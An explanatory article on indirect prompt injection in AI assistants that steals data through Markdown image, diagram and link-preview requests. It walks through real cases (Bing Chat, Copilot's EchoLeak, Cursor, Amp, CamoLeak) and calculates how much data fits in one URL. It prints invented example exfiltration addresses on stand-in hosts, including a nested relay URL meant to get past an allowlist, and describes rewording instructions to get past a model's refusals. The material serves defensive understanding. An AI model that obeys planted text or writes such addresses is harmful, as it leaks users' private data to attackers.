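# Data theft through image requests in AI applications, and why firewalls and security monitoring miss it

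## Background: AI applications, planted instructions and the tools that watch web traffic

Data theft through image requests is an attack on software built around large language models, the systems behind chatbots and AI assistants. The attacker puts instructions in an email, a document or a web page and waits for someone's assistant to read them. If the attack works, the model writes a web address containing private data, and the software tries to load that address as an image. This sends the data to the attacker's server, where the attacker reads it from the log. Since 2023, researchers have found versions of this flaw in products from OpenAI, Microsoft, Google and Anthropic, among others. Most companies have several tools that inspect web traffic, but a single image request looks like the thousands of others an office produces in a day.

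### How an assistant assembles its context

An AI-integrated application passes a user's requests and any retrieved content to a language model, then shows or acts on the model's output. Before each answer, the application combines everything the model will receive into one body of text, called the context. The context usually includes the developer's instructions for the assistant, the user's request and the conversation so far. It also includes whatever the application fetched to handle the request, such as emails, files, search results or web pages.

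All of this reaches the model as a single sequence of tokens, the short fragments of text that a language model processes. The model works by predicting the next token from the ones before it. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, traces the security problem to this. A sentence from the developer and one from a stranger's email go through the same prediction process, and current models enforce no security boundary between them.

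His title makes a comparison with SQL injection, an older flaw that most web developers know. Programs use SQL to query databases. In an SQL injection attack, someone types a fragment of SQL into a web form, and a carelessly written application passes it to the database as part of a command. Developers can reliably prevent this with parameterised queries, which send the command and the user's input to the database separately, so the database engine cannot run the input as a command. David C argues that language models have no equivalent because they do not take instructions and data separately. He thinks it very possible that developers will never fully fix this weakness.

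Developers try to mark the parts of the context by putting delimiters around retrieved documents, labelling each passage with its role and telling the model to ignore any instructions inside the documents. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes these as useful engineering practices but not a hard security boundary. It also lists more ambitious ideas, including regions of the context with fixed types and external policy engines that decide which content may authorise an action. Researchers are also training models to respect labels such as "untrusted document", but it is difficult to make the labels change the model's behaviour reliably. If a label works only most of the time, an attacker can try again with different wording.

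### Indirect prompt injection

Prompt injection is the general name for attacks that exploit this mixing of trusted and untrusted text. The security company Preamble reported the behaviour to OpenAI in May 2022, according to the security researcher Johann Rehberger's *Trust No AI* (2024). The programmer Simon Willison named it later that year. In the early cases, the attacker was usually the user, trying to make a chatbot break its rules or reveal its hidden instructions.

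In *Not what you've signed up for*, Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) described indirect prompt injection, a version of the attack that matters far more for data theft. Without interacting with the application, the attacker plants instructions in content that the model will later read on someone else's behalf, and the model follows them as if the user had given them. The team demonstrated attacks on real products, including the GPT-4 version of Microsoft's Bing Chat. Bing Chat's sidebar in the Edge browser could read the page a user had open, and the team found that text on the page could steer the model even when the user couldn't see it.

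Their survey of delivery routes is still a good guide to the sources of planted text. An attacker can put the text on a public website or in a social media post and wait for a search to retrieve it, perhaps using search engine optimisation to raise the page's ranking. Email is more direct, since the attacker chooses the recipient. A person may also introduce the text unknowingly by copying something from the attacker's site into a chatbot. If the model accepts images, the attacker can put the instructions in one. A short first instruction can also make the model fetch a longer one from elsewhere. In an office example from David C, a job applicant hides a line in a CV instructing the recruiter's screening system to approve it.

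Later work has mostly made the definition more precise. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) describes three parties: a user with a legitimate task, an agent acting for that user, and an external source that the agent consults. The attacker needs to control only some of the external content. The harm arises because text from the source directs the agent, although the source has no authority to do so. Like the earlier papers, *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) traces the weakness to developer instructions and third-party data sharing one natural-language context. It adds that the potential harm grows when the application can navigate pages and choose tools, since the planted text can then cause actions as well as bad answers.

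Planted instructions do not always succeed. Models behave differently from run to run, and training and careful marking of untrusted text lower the odds. David C accepts that such measures help, but he warns against filters that look for known bad phrases, because an attacker can endlessly reword an instruction. He prefers to treat the model as a "confused deputy", the security term for a component with high privileges that an outsider can trick into using them on the outsider's behalf. On that view, the designer should assume that the trick will sometimes work and use ordinary non-AI controls to limit what the application can then do.

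### Three conditions for theft

Whether planted instructions can lead to data theft depends on what the AI application can do. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) named three capabilities that together make theft possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside world.

Suppose an employee asks an assistant each morning to summarise her unread email. The application fetches the new messages and puts them into the model's context. They include a draft contract, a note from the payroll department and a message from a stranger. The contract and the payroll note are private data, and the stranger's message is untrusted content. Anyone who knows her address can send her such a message without breaking into anything. If the message contains instructions and the model follows them, the model can pick out figures from the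 contract, because both are in the same context. Whether the figures then leave the company depends on what the application can do with the model's output.

The most obvious way for an assistant to send data out is by email, so a cautious developer might withhold that ability or require the employee to confirm each message. Willison's definition of outward communication also covers any tool that can make a web request, including one that loads an image, and even a link that the user might click. An assistant that can only display text and pictures may therefore meet all three conditions, even though its developer believes it cannot send anything.

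Published cases suggest that developers have often missed this. Willison linked to fourteen demonstrations of data theft from AI products, including ChatGPT, Slack and Amazon Q, between April 2023 and February 2025, and to three more from the weeks before he wrote. Rehberger called image loading from untrusted sites one of the most common security flaws in applications of this kind and named eleven products in which he had found and reported it. These cases were found by people looking for the flaw, so they can't be used to estimate how common it is across AI products, but they show that large companies with experienced security staff have repeatedly made the same mistake.

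According to Willison, vendors fixed almost all of these flaws promptly, usually by closing the route by which data left. The inbox assistant needs both private data and untrusted content to summarise email from strangers, so the outward route is the condition a developer can most easily remove while keeping the product useful.

### Out-of-band channels before AI

Security specialists call a path like this an out-of-band channel, meaning that data reaches the attacker outside the normal exchange between user and application. The term predates AI assistants, and web security testers have used the idea for many years.

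*Data Retrieval over DNS in SQL Injection Attacks* (Štampar, 2013) sorts SQL injection techniques by how the stolen data travels. With in-band techniques, the attacker reads the result in the web page the application returns or in an error message. With inference techniques, the attacker asks the database a long series of yes-or-no questions and works out each answer from a small change in the page or a delay in its arrival, without ever transferring the data itself. Out-of-band techniques use a different channel. In one variant, the database puts a query's result in a parameter of a web request to a server the attacker controls, and the attacker reads it from that server's log files.

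When an AI assistant leaks data through an image address, the flow is almost the same, with the language model in place of the database. Štampar noted that out-of-band techniques were less widely used than the others, mostly because they were complicated to set up. The attacker has less to set up in an AI application that loads images automatically, because the developer has already built the part that makes the outside request.

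Testers adopted the same idea to confirm flaws that they could not see in an application's responses. The security software company PortSwigger calls SQL injection "blind" when those responses contain neither the query's results nor any database error. A related flaw, server-side request forgery (SSRF), lets an outsider make an application's server send web requests to an address the outsider chooses. PortSwigger's *Blind SSRF vulnerabilities* describes the blind form, in which the server sends the request but the application's response contains nothing from the reply.

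Testers solve this with a callback. They submit an input that will make the application contact their own server if the flaw exists, and then "patiently listen" (Kettle, *Hunting asynchronous vulnerabilities*). Stuttard (2015), in *Introducing Burp Collaborator*, announced a PortSwigger product that automated the method. Each test carries a unique random name under a domain that PortSwigger controls, so any contact with that name identifies the test that caused it, even if the contact is just a lookup in the domain name system (DNS), the internet's directory of site names. Stuttard remarked that network filters seldom block these lookups, because servers need DNS and administrators almost always allow outbound DNS traffic. In *OAST (Out-of-band Application Security Testing)*, Stuttard (2017) wrote that the most skilled testers had long done this by hand, on private servers, and that a callback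 might arrive days after the test.

A tester's callback normally carries only the random identifier, which is enough to prove that the request happened. A thief uses the same path but replaces the identifier with stolen data. Defenders face the same difficulty as testers, because the application's reply to the user may look normal while the evidence is in a separate request to another server.

### The tracking pixel

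The image part of the attack has a precursor in the tracking pixel, which most people with an email account have received. A tracking pixel is a picture, usually very small and of no value to the reader, that the sender of an email stores on a remote server. France's data protection authority, CNIL, explains how it works in its *Recommendation on Tracking Pixels in Emails*, published in April 2026 according to Inside Privacy's *CNIL Publishes Recommendation on Email Tracking Pixels*. To display the picture, the recipient's email program has to request it from the address given in the message. That address usually contains parameters unique to the recipient, so the sender can identify who opened the email from the parameters in the request.

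Englehardt, Han and Narayanan (2018), in *I never signed up for this!*, measured how often mailing-list emails leak recipients' addresses to third parties. They built a crawler that signed up for mailing lists, collected 12,618 emails from 902 senders and simulated a person reading them. About 85 percent of the emails contained third-party content. About 29 percent sent the recipient's email address to at least one third party, encoded as a parameter in the URL of the embedded content, and the researchers judged 62 percent of these leaks intentional. Some senders scrambled the email address with a hash function, so the researchers had to test combinations of encodings and hashes to find it in the traffic. Anyone searching network traffic for data leaked by an AI assistant faces a similar problem, and also does not know in advance which data to look for.

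By then, email programs routinely removed scripts from messages but still loaded images. Pixels on websites have since grown more elaborate. In 2023, the US Federal Trade Commission (FTC) described how the term had come to cover a broad range of web code that can report purchases and even text that people type into forms. It had just taken action against two digital health companies, GoodRx and BetterHelp, over health data that they allegedly shared for advertising. A simple email pixel reveals less, because the sender writes the image address before sending the message and can include only what they already know about the recipient. The request then adds a few technical details, such as the time and the recipient's network address. In the AI version, the model writes the address after it has read the private data, so the address can include that data.

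### Where the security tools sit

Suppose the employee with the full inbox opens her assistant in a browser at the office. Her request leaves the company through a secure web gateway, a proxy that inspects and logs employees' outgoing web traffic. The company may also run data loss prevention (DLP) tools, which search outgoing data for sensitive patterns such as card numbers or access keys. MITRE ATT&CK's *Data Loss Prevention* (2020), an entry in a public catalogue of attack techniques and countermeasures, notes that DLP can be part of a firewall or a separate product, running on the network or on individual machines.

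At the other end of the connection, a web application firewall (WAF) often sits in front of the assistant's own servers. It inspects traffic to the web application and, in some products, the application's responses. It is usually used to stop attacks on the application, such as SQL injection.

The application then sends its answer back to the browser. The site can include a Content Security Policy (CSP), which lists the hosts from which the browser may load images and other content. Rehberger recommends such a policy as one way to stop an AI application from loading images from untrusted sites. The renderer is the part of the application that turns the model's text into a displayed page. If the answer contains an image address and no rule blocks it, the renderer causes the browser to request the image. This request is new outgoing traffic, or egress. It goes from the employee's browser to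 the host in the address, so it passes through the company's gateway but normally bypasses the WAF, which guards a different server.

The security operations centre (SOC) behind these tools is the team and systems that collect an organisation's logs, raise alerts and investigate them. MITRE's *11 Strategies of a World-Class Cybersecurity Operations Center* (2022) warns that most organisations generate more data than a SOC can process, so its staff must choose what to collect. It also says that records from individual machines are generally more informative than network traffic for detecting intrusions. A SOC that keeps no record of image requests, or keeps only the host name from each address, will have little to investigate.

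This path assumes an office where all traffic leaves through one gateway, and fewer companies now work that way. *Guide to a Secure Enterprise Network Landscape* (Chandramouli, 2022), written for the US standards agency NIST, lists the loss of a protectable network perimeter among the effects of cloud services and scattered offices. Employees reach the same applications from homes, hotels and cafes. If the employee is at home and her laptop does not send its traffic through the gateway, the gateway has no record of the image request. When the AI provider's own servers fetch the picture, the request never crosses her employer's network.

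## How an image request carries data out

### From planted text to a server log

Suppose the employee's unread emails include one from a colleague with a 40-character access key for a test server, and one from a stranger with instructions for her AI assistant.

Both messages enter the context when she asks for her morning summary. The theft fails here if the application leaves the stranger's message out, for example by summarising only mail from known senders. But applications also retrieve text that nobody asked for. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested an assistant that automatically previews any web address in a conversation. The preview adds the page's title and description to the context, and the team planted instructions in them. In 480 runs with a small open-weight model, the assistant sent a secret from its context to a test server about 89 percent of the time,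 using a web-request tool rather than an image. The team had put the secret directly into a context with few other instructions, so the figure describes an assistant with almost no defences.

The model next has to pick out something private from its context, which already contains the colleague's key. In August 2024, Rehberger uploaded a batch of employee reviews to Google AI Studio, a site for trying out Google's models. One review contained hidden instructions to summarize every file in the batch and put each summary in its own image address (Willison, 2024, *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo*).

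An assistant with tools can also fetch private data that is not yet in the context. Rehberger demonstrated this on Amp, Sourcegraph's coding assistant, and described it in *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code* on his blog, Embrace the Red. A comment in a source file made Amp open a configuration file containing secrets and send out the contents in an image address. The underlying model sometimes refused to read and leak sensitive information, so Rehberger had to reword the instructions. Limiting which files the assistant can open is more dependable than relying on refusals, because the limit works however the attacker words the request.

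The model then writes its answer. Many chat applications accept Markdown, a notation in which a few punctuation marks turn a line into a heading, a link or an image. For an image, the model writes a caption and an address, and in this theft the address ends with the key. With an invented value, and a host under .example, an ending reserved for documentation, it might look like this:

`https://pictures.example/logo.png?ref=INVENTED-VALUE`

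The application can still catch the address by checking the answer before displaying it. The model may also get the address wrong. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) describes a test that gives half marks if the model writes the address but leaves the placeholders unfilled. When the researchers ran the test on a report-writing agent, the finished report included the links specified in the planted text.

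Next, the renderer converts the Markdown into an HTML image tag, and the browser requests the address without waiting for a click. In one of Rehberger's earliest cases, described in Embrace the Red's *Bing Chat*, the planted text told the model to wait two turns before writing the image, so the leak came well after the model had read the attacker's page. The data leaves with the request, so the theft succeeds even if no picture comes back. Any picture that does come back can be a single transparent pixel, as Rehberger showed with another coding tool in Embrace the Red's *Windsurf*. The application can prevent the request by removing images, asking the user before loading them or accepting only approved hosts, although in EchoLeak, CamoLeak and SearchLeak a trusted service passed the data on.

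Finally, the attacker's server logs the request, typically with the time, the sender's network address, the path and query, and the browser's name and version. Embrace the Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* shows one such line from September 2023. One parameter holds the stolen item, a web link, and the rest of the line describes an ordinary Firefox browser on a Mac. At this point nobody can get the data back. The company can cancel a stolen key before the attacker uses it, but it can't do anything similar for stolen contract figures.

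### How much fits in one address

Three parts of a web address can carry data to another computer: the hostname, the path and the query. This invented address has the same value in all three:

`https://VALUE.pictures.example/VALUE/logo.png?ref=VALUE`

The query is the part after the question mark. A web server can ignore it and return the same picture every time, so the attacker needs only an ordinary server that logs requests. The path works equally well if the server returns one picture for every path. In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Willison describes two attacks that used the path, one from 2025 on GitLab's assistant Duo and one from 2024 on Mistral's chatbot LeChat. The attacker can't use the part after a hash sign, which marks a position within a page, because browsers do not send it.

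A value in the hostname can leave through the DNS lookup, which testers' callbacks also use. An attacker who owns a domain can run the server that answers lookups for every name under it, so the value can reach them even if a firewall blocks the connection that follows. Hostnames have less room for data, however, because they allow at most 63 characters between dots and about 250 in total, and DNS doesn't distinguish capital from lowercase letters.

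No single rule limits the length of a whole address, but developers often stay below about 2,000 characters so that all common software will accept it. If the hostname, file name and other fixed parts take 100 characters, 1,900 remain for data. An attacker can have the model write the data in Base64url, an encoding that uses 64 characters, all of them safe in an address: capital and small letters, digits, the hyphen and the underscore. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026), a study of models that an attacker has tampered with, used this encoding because it suits URL parameters and avoids conspicuous characters. Since 64 is 2 to the power of 6, each character represents 6 bits:

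1,900 characters × 6 bits = 11,400 bits

11,400 bits ÷ 8 = 1,425 bytes

The colleague's 40-character key, at one byte per character, contains 320 bits and takes up 54 characters in Base64url, less than 3 percent of the available space. One address could hold 35 such keys, or roughly 240 words of English. If the key consists only of letters and digits, the model can copy it into the address unchanged, which takes 40 characters and avoids encoding errors. Hostnames ignore capitalization, so a hostname encoding usually carries 5 bits per character, and the same key needs 64 characters. The attacker would have to split it, because at most 63 characters fit between two dots.

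Larger amounts of data can be split across several requests, and a 10,000-byte contract would need eight. Lan and colleagues also split secrets to make each request less revealing, which lowered their measure of leakage in a single request by 73 percent and got past simple DLP checks. A cap on address length therefore slows theft but doesn't prevent it. An address with only 200 usable characters still holds 150 bytes, enough for three keys.

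### Comparison with legitimate requests

Browsers routinely load pictures from long, complicated addresses. A signed cloud-storage link gives temporary access to a private file and includes a signature, a code the storage provider uses to check that the link is genuine. An analytics pixel reports a visit to a page. A chart service draws a graph from numbers in the address and returns it as a picture. The table compares a typical request of each kind with the theft of the colleague's key.

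| Field | Stolen key | Signed storage link | Analytics pixel | Chart service |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Method | GET | GET | Usually GET | Usually GET |
| Host | A server whose log the attacker can read | Storage provider | Analytics company | Chart company |
| Path | `/logo.png` | `/team/photo.png` | `/pixel.gif` | `/bar` |
| Query | One parameter containing the key | Expiry time, account identifier, signature | Visitor number, page title, page address | Labels and values for the graph |
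| Length of query | 40 to 60 characters | Often several hundred | Often several hundred | Grows with the data |
| Looks random | Yes | Yes, in the signature | In part | Usually not |
| Reply | Any picture, or none | The stored picture | A tiny picture, or none | The finished graph |

A filter that looks for random text would flag many harmless requests. Signed links commonly use a 256-bit signature, which takes 43 characters in Base64url and looks random by design. The encoded key takes 54 characters and looks much the same. If the attacker steals a short summary in plain English instead, the address looks less random than a signed link and more like a page title or chart labels. Filtering by length works no better, because the stolen key is shorter than many legitimate queries, and a signed link made with temporary credentials can include a session token of several hundred characters.

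The attacker also chooses the file name and the parameter names, so an image request can imitate a tracking pixel or a signed link. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* describes a similar attack, in which the outgoing request resembles a normal query to a search service.

Another problem with searching outgoing requests for private text is that AI chat sites already send such text to other companies. *Penny for Your Prompts* (Bekos, Tsouvalas et al., 2026) tested 42 of these sites in May 2026. On the 25 general-purpose ones, each prompt led to an average of 540 outgoing requests, 118 of them to trackers. Thirteen of the 25 sent the title of the user's conversation to a tracker, and four sent the prompt word for word. Eleven of those thirteen also sent a tracker the user's email address. This happened without an attacker, because the sites had installed analytics scripts that read the text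 from the page as they would on a news site. *Tracking Conversations* (Jazlan, Wang et al.) similarly found that 17 of 20 chatbots shared data with at least one outside company.

Trackers can also send data in the body of a request, so only part of this traffic resembles an image request. Still, when an analyst finds a user's words being sent to an unfamiliar company, the cause will often be advertising technology. The host is more useful for distinguishing theft from advertising, since a company can list the storage, analytics and chart providers it expects to see. But the host doesn't help either if the attacker finds a way to send the data through one of those providers.

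### HTML images, diagrams and link previews

Anything an application loads automatically can carry data, just as a Markdown image can. Some applications accept HTML in the model's output, and an HTML image tag produces the same request. In the GitLab Duo case, according to Willison, instructions hidden in a public project made the assistant read a private code change and put it in the address of an HTML image.

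Diagrams are easier to overlook because developers don't usually think of them as a source of web requests. Mermaid notation turns text into flowcharts, and a box in the chart can contain an image. In June 2025, Rehberger reported that Cursor, an AI code editor, loaded these images without the user's approval. Embrace the Red's *Cursor IDE* shows planted text in a source file making the editor search a project for access keys and send one out through a diagram. Rehberger noted that the diagram simply appeared, so the developer had no chance to notice a long address while the model was writing it.

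In *Takedown*, a broader study, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) at the South Korean university KAIST found the same type of flaw. They examined eight widely used coding agents, which they kept anonymous while the vendors dealt with the reports. They intercepted messages between the agents and their models, read the source code where it was public and reverse-engineered some of the other agents. They identified 15 security issues. One agent, labelled A2, had a Mermaid renderer that requested images from outside servers without the user's approval.

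The researchers then built a complete attack on A2. A user asks the agent to fetch problem reports from a shared software project, and one report contains planted instructions. Following them, the agent opens a settings file elsewhere on the user's computer, which it can do without asking permission, and finds an access key. It writes a diagram with the key in an image address, and drawing the diagram sends the key to the attacker. The researchers tested this on a private project. When they reported the renderer flaw, the vendor classed it as a duplicate, so someone else had already found it.

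A2 was the only agent in which they reported a leak through a renderer, but four of the eight agents allowed an outsider to steal files from anywhere on the machine without the user's approval. Another agent, A4, had a web-fetch tool that needed no approval and could also send out data. Fixing a renderer therefore closes only one of the ways data can leave a coding agent. A2's renderer was easy to miss because these agents usually rely on the user to approve risky actions, and drawing a diagram did not count as one.

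Messaging apps can also make the request when they preview links. Slack, Discord and Teams automatically contact the site behind a posted link to show a preview of the page. If planted text makes a chatbot post a link containing private data, fetching the preview sends the data to that site before anyone clicks, as Rehberger pointed out in 2024.

The delay before the image loads can be longer. In a case Willison described in May 2026, Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval, and images in those messages loaded when the user opened them. Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) reports a similar finding by the security company PromptArmor. A chatbot could show its user nothing harmful, but data would leak later when a developer opened the conversation in OpenAI's log viewer, which loaded the image.

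### From chatbots in 2023 to coding tools in 2025

Rehberger and Roman Samoilenko independently discovered the flaw in ChatGPT in the spring of 2023, according to SecurityWeek. In Samoilenko's version, a website added instructions to any text a visitor copied from it, and the visitor pasted them into ChatGPT without noticing. Willison (2023) described this version in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* that April.

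Rehberger reported the flaw in Bing Chat to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and in ChatGPT to OpenAI the next day. Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed the flaw, while OpenAI decided not to fix it, according to Embrace the Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*. Anthropic fixed the flaw in Claude, and Microsoft fixed it again in a second product, according to Rehberger in Embrace the Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*. In December 2023, OpenAI began checking whether an image address was safe before ChatGPT displayed the image (Willison, 2023, *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*).

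Five of the eleven products on the list Rehberger published in December 2024 were Google's (Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio and Colab), and three were Microsoft's (Bing Chat, Azure AI and GitHub Copilot Chat). The others were ChatGPT, Claude and Discord. Google and Microsoft had each fixed the flaw in one product before Rehberger found it in another, so teams within the same company did not reliably learn from each other.

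In 2025, many of the reports concerned coding tools, which can often read access keys stored on a developer's machine. Rehberger ran a series that August called the Month of AI Bugs, and Embrace the Red's *Wrap Up* lists 29 posts. The posts covered many kinds of flaw, including image or diagram requests that leaked data from Cursor, Amp and Windsurf. Embrace the Red's *Google Jules* named image rendering as one of several ways to get data out of Google's coding agent. Rehberger had contacted Sourcegraph about the Amp flaw on 14 June, and the company fixed it quickly.

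The security company VerSprite found the flaw in Continue, an open-source assistant for the code editor Visual Studio Code. VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* compares two routes. If the planted text was in a code file, asking the assistant to analyze that file was enough to send the data out. If it was on a web page, the user first had to approve the assistant's request to fetch the page, but that approval did not cover the image request that followed, which carried the data out. VerSprite reported the flaw on 20 August 2025, and the next day the developers released a corrected version that asks for confirmation before loading external images and restricts access to certain files.

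Cursor needed two attempts to fix the flaw. It released the first fix in version 1.3 on 29 July 2025. The official record, MITRE's *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025), gives the flaw a medium severity score but rates its effect on confidentiality as high. According to CVELogic's *CVE-2025-61589* (2025), researchers then found ways around the fix, and Cursor closed them in version 1.7.

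### Why vendors keep repeating the mistake

Most of these reports come from outsiders who did not see how the products were built, so any explanation is partly inference. One likely cause is that software that displays Markdown normally loads images. In an ordinary document editor, the person who writes the text chooses the images, but in an AI application a stranger can influence the text, and a standard renderer displays it in the same way. The problem was still present in ChatGPT in May 2026, when The Hacker News (2026) reported that Permiso Security had found the renderer automatically loading images whose addresses came from a page the assistant had just summarised.

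The evidence is firmer that companies fix one renderer and miss another. OpenAI's December 2023 check did not protect ChatGPT's mobile apps, and the macOS app released in 2024 also lacked it, according to Rehberger. Anthropic fixed Claude in 2023 but had to fix a similar leak in its iOS app in 2024. Both companies already knew about the flaw, so lack of awareness does not explain why it recurred.

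Some vendors have disputed that the behaviour is a flaw. In Willison's collection, xAI closed Rehberger's reports about its Grok chatbot as "Informational", and Google told a researcher that image loading in its Antigravity coding tool was "intended behavior". Google also listed data theft through planted instructions among the tool's known issues and said it was working on them. Some vendors told Lee and colleagues that certain findings fell outside their security requirements, largely because the user starts the task that triggers the attack. Other companies, such as Windsurf, stopped replying. VerSprite's *Another Day, Another Leak* reports that the company behind the coding assistant CodeGPT never replied.

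*Agentic ProbLLMs* (2026), a conference paper based on the Month of AI Bugs, argues that vendors are coming to treat insecure designs as normal while shifting responsibility to users. It warns of a "normalization of deviance", in which people live with a risky practice for so long that they stop noticing it. This is not true of every vendor, since Amp and Continue were fixed quickly, though in both cases after an outsider reported the problem.

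As assistants gained access to more data, delays in fixing flaws put more of it at risk. In August 2025, Rehberger got around ChatGPT's image check again and sent out parts of a user's earlier conversations, which OpenAI had by then begun adding to the context. Embrace the Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* says he had reported the gap in October 2024 and the underlying flaw more than two years before the August 2025 bypass.

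## How trusted services pass the data on

The simplest defence against these leaks is a Content Security Policy that lets the browser load images only from approved hosts. Even if planted text gets the model to write the colleague's access key into an image address, the browser never contacts the attacker's server. Microsoft 365 Copilot, GitHub's Copilot Chat and the email program Superhuman all had such policies in 2025, but researchers still got data out of all three.

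### What an attacker needs from an approved host

An allowlist limits the attacker to approved hosts. The attacker can still choose the rest of the address, but the request will go to a server run by Microsoft, Google or GitHub, whose logs the attacker can't read. The attacker therefore needs an approved host that will either pass the data on or store it somewhere they can read it.

A relay passes it on. Many reputable services fetch an address when someone asks them to. A messaging service does it to preview a link, and a search engine may do it to analyse a picture. The attacker takes the address of such a service and puts a second address, containing the stolen value, in one of its parameters. With invented hosts, the result might look like this:

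`https://preview.trusted.example/fetch?url=https://collector.example/INVENTED-VALUE`

The browser compares the outer address with the allowlist, finds `preview.trusted.example` there and sends the request. It doesn't check the nested address, because a Content Security Policy ignores everything after the question mark. The relay's servers then read the parameter and request the nested address, and the attacker's log records the value.

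The theft now involves two requests. The first goes from the victim's computer to the relay, and the second goes from the relay's data centre to the attacker without crossing the victim's network. A gateway that does not decrypt web traffic can detect only a connection to a familiar service. A gateway that decrypts the traffic can record the nested address, but someone still has to look for it.

Web security specialists knew about this weakness long before AI assistants. GitHub (2017) described asking the security firm Cure53 what an attacker could do after finding a way to insert content into a GitHub page. GitHub had already shortened its image allowlist, but the list still included Google Analytics and the profile-picture service Gravatar. Cure53 inserted an image tag with an opening quotation mark and no closing one. The browser treated everything up to the next matching quotation mark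 as part of the image address, including any secret in between.

Gravatar relayed requests to other addresses. A website could specify a fallback picture hosted elsewhere, and when Gravatar had no profile picture to show, it redirected the browser to a proxy that fetched the fallback. The proxy's host was also on GitHub's allowlist. Google Analytics could record the secret itself. An attacker with an account there could have the image request report an "event" with the secret in its description, which would then appear in the attacker's statistics. GitHub removed both services from its image allowlist.

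In an AI application, the model replaces the unclosed quotation mark and is more effective, because it can search the context for something valuable and leave out the rest. In an early example from 2023, Google's chatbot Bard loaded images only from Google's own hosts. Willison explained in *Hacking Google Bard* that anyone could use Google Apps Script to run a small program on one of those hosts and collect whatever the image request contained. Google said it had fixed the reported flaw.

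An allowlist can also go out of date. Salesforce's assistant Agentforce still accepted images from a domain whose registration had expired, according to Willison's account of the ForcedLeak attack in September 2025. Researchers at Noma Security registered the domain themselves and received data about sales leads in their server logs. Salesforce corrected the list and added a separate check on the links its assistant could write. A routine check of domain ownership would have caught this mistake, but it would not have flagged Microsoft Teams or Bing, which belonged to the right company and were working as designed.

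### EchoLeak: a link-fetching service in Microsoft Teams

Researchers at the security company Aim Security built a working attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot in January 2025 and reported it to Microsoft. Ravia, the head of their team, explained it in detail after the fix in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (2025). The attacker only had to email the victim, from any address, and the victim did not have to open the message.

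Before answering a question, Copilot retrieves relevant material from the employee's mailbox, files and Teams chats. An attacker cannot see the question in advance, so the email has to seem relevant to many possible questions. Aim's researchers wrote a long email with separate sections on routine office subjects such as onboarding and leave. Retrieval systems often split long texts into pieces and compare each piece with the question, so each section gave the email another chance of being retrieved. In the team's demonstration, Copilot retrieved it for questions on various topics.

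Microsoft had put a classifier in front of the model to catch planted instructions. The email got past it because its instructions were addressed to the human recipient and it never mentioned Copilot or AI. Ravia adds that developers have few realistic examples to train such classifiers on.

Microsoft also used a filter to remove outside links and images from Copilot's answers. The filter recognised the common Markdown notation, in which the address directly follows the caption, but not a second one, in which the address appears on a separate line, like a footnote. The renderer did recognise the second notation, so the image stayed in the answer. That left the Content Security Policy as the only obstacle.

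The policy's image list had about thirty distinct entries, and several allowed every host under a domain. The researchers searched the approved domains for a service that would fetch an outside address. They first found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. They then found a service in Teams that fetches the content behind a link. It needed no invitation, which made the attack zero-click.

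The first request went to a host under `asyncgw.teams.microsoft.com`, which *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) identifies as a Teams preview service. Computers in an office that uses Microsoft 365 contact Teams all day. The attacker's host appeared only as a parameter in the URL. Reddy and Gujral worked from public material and did not reproduce the attack. They leave open whether the attacker's log would show the network address of a Microsoft server or that of the victim. Ravia describes the server making the fetch, which suggests the log would show Microsoft's address.

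Anything in Copilot's context was at risk, including the chat history and whatever Copilot had retrieved from email, files and Teams. The attacker did not need to know what data the company had, because the attacker's email instructed Copilot to pick the most sensitive item it could find. Copilot was also instructed not to cite the email as a source, so an employee who noticed something odd in the answer would have had no reference leading back to it.

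Microsoft began fixing the flaw in April 2025, finished the work on its own servers in May and published an advisory on 11 June, according to Reddy and Gujral. Customers did not need to install anything, and Ravia knew of no administrator setting that would have stopped the attack before the fix. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips the footnote-style links and embedded images from outside content before the model reads it. That would stop an attacker from supplying a ready-made image in this notation, but it would not make the Teams service any safer as a relay.

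SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reported that EchoLeak received a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 and that Microsoft said nobody had exploited it. Microsoft's statement is stronger evidence than the absence of customer complaints, because Microsoft ran the relay and could check its own records for suspicious fetches. A customer's logs would have shown little except visits to Teams.

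### CamoLeak: GitHub's signed image proxy

Reddy and Gujral list a signed image proxy among the measures they expect to stop an attack like EchoLeak, although they did not test it. Such a proxy fetches outside images for users but accepts only addresses with a valid signature, so an attacker cannot simply insert a new address containing stolen data. In June 2025, a researcher at Legit Security found a way to send data through GitHub's proxy, which had used this design for years.

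GitHub built its image proxy, later named Camo, to prevent the warnings browsers displayed when a secure page loaded an insecure picture. People could trigger these warnings by including pictures from other sites in their comments and project pages. GitHub's *Sidejack Prevention Phase 3* (2010) describes how the company rewrote each image address so that the picture came through its own servers. Camo later became part of GitHub's defence against data leaks, when Cure53's findings led the company to send Gravatar pictures through it as well.

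A Camo address has two parts after the host name:

`https://camo.githubusercontent.com/SIGNATURE/ENCODED-ORIGINAL-ADDRESS`

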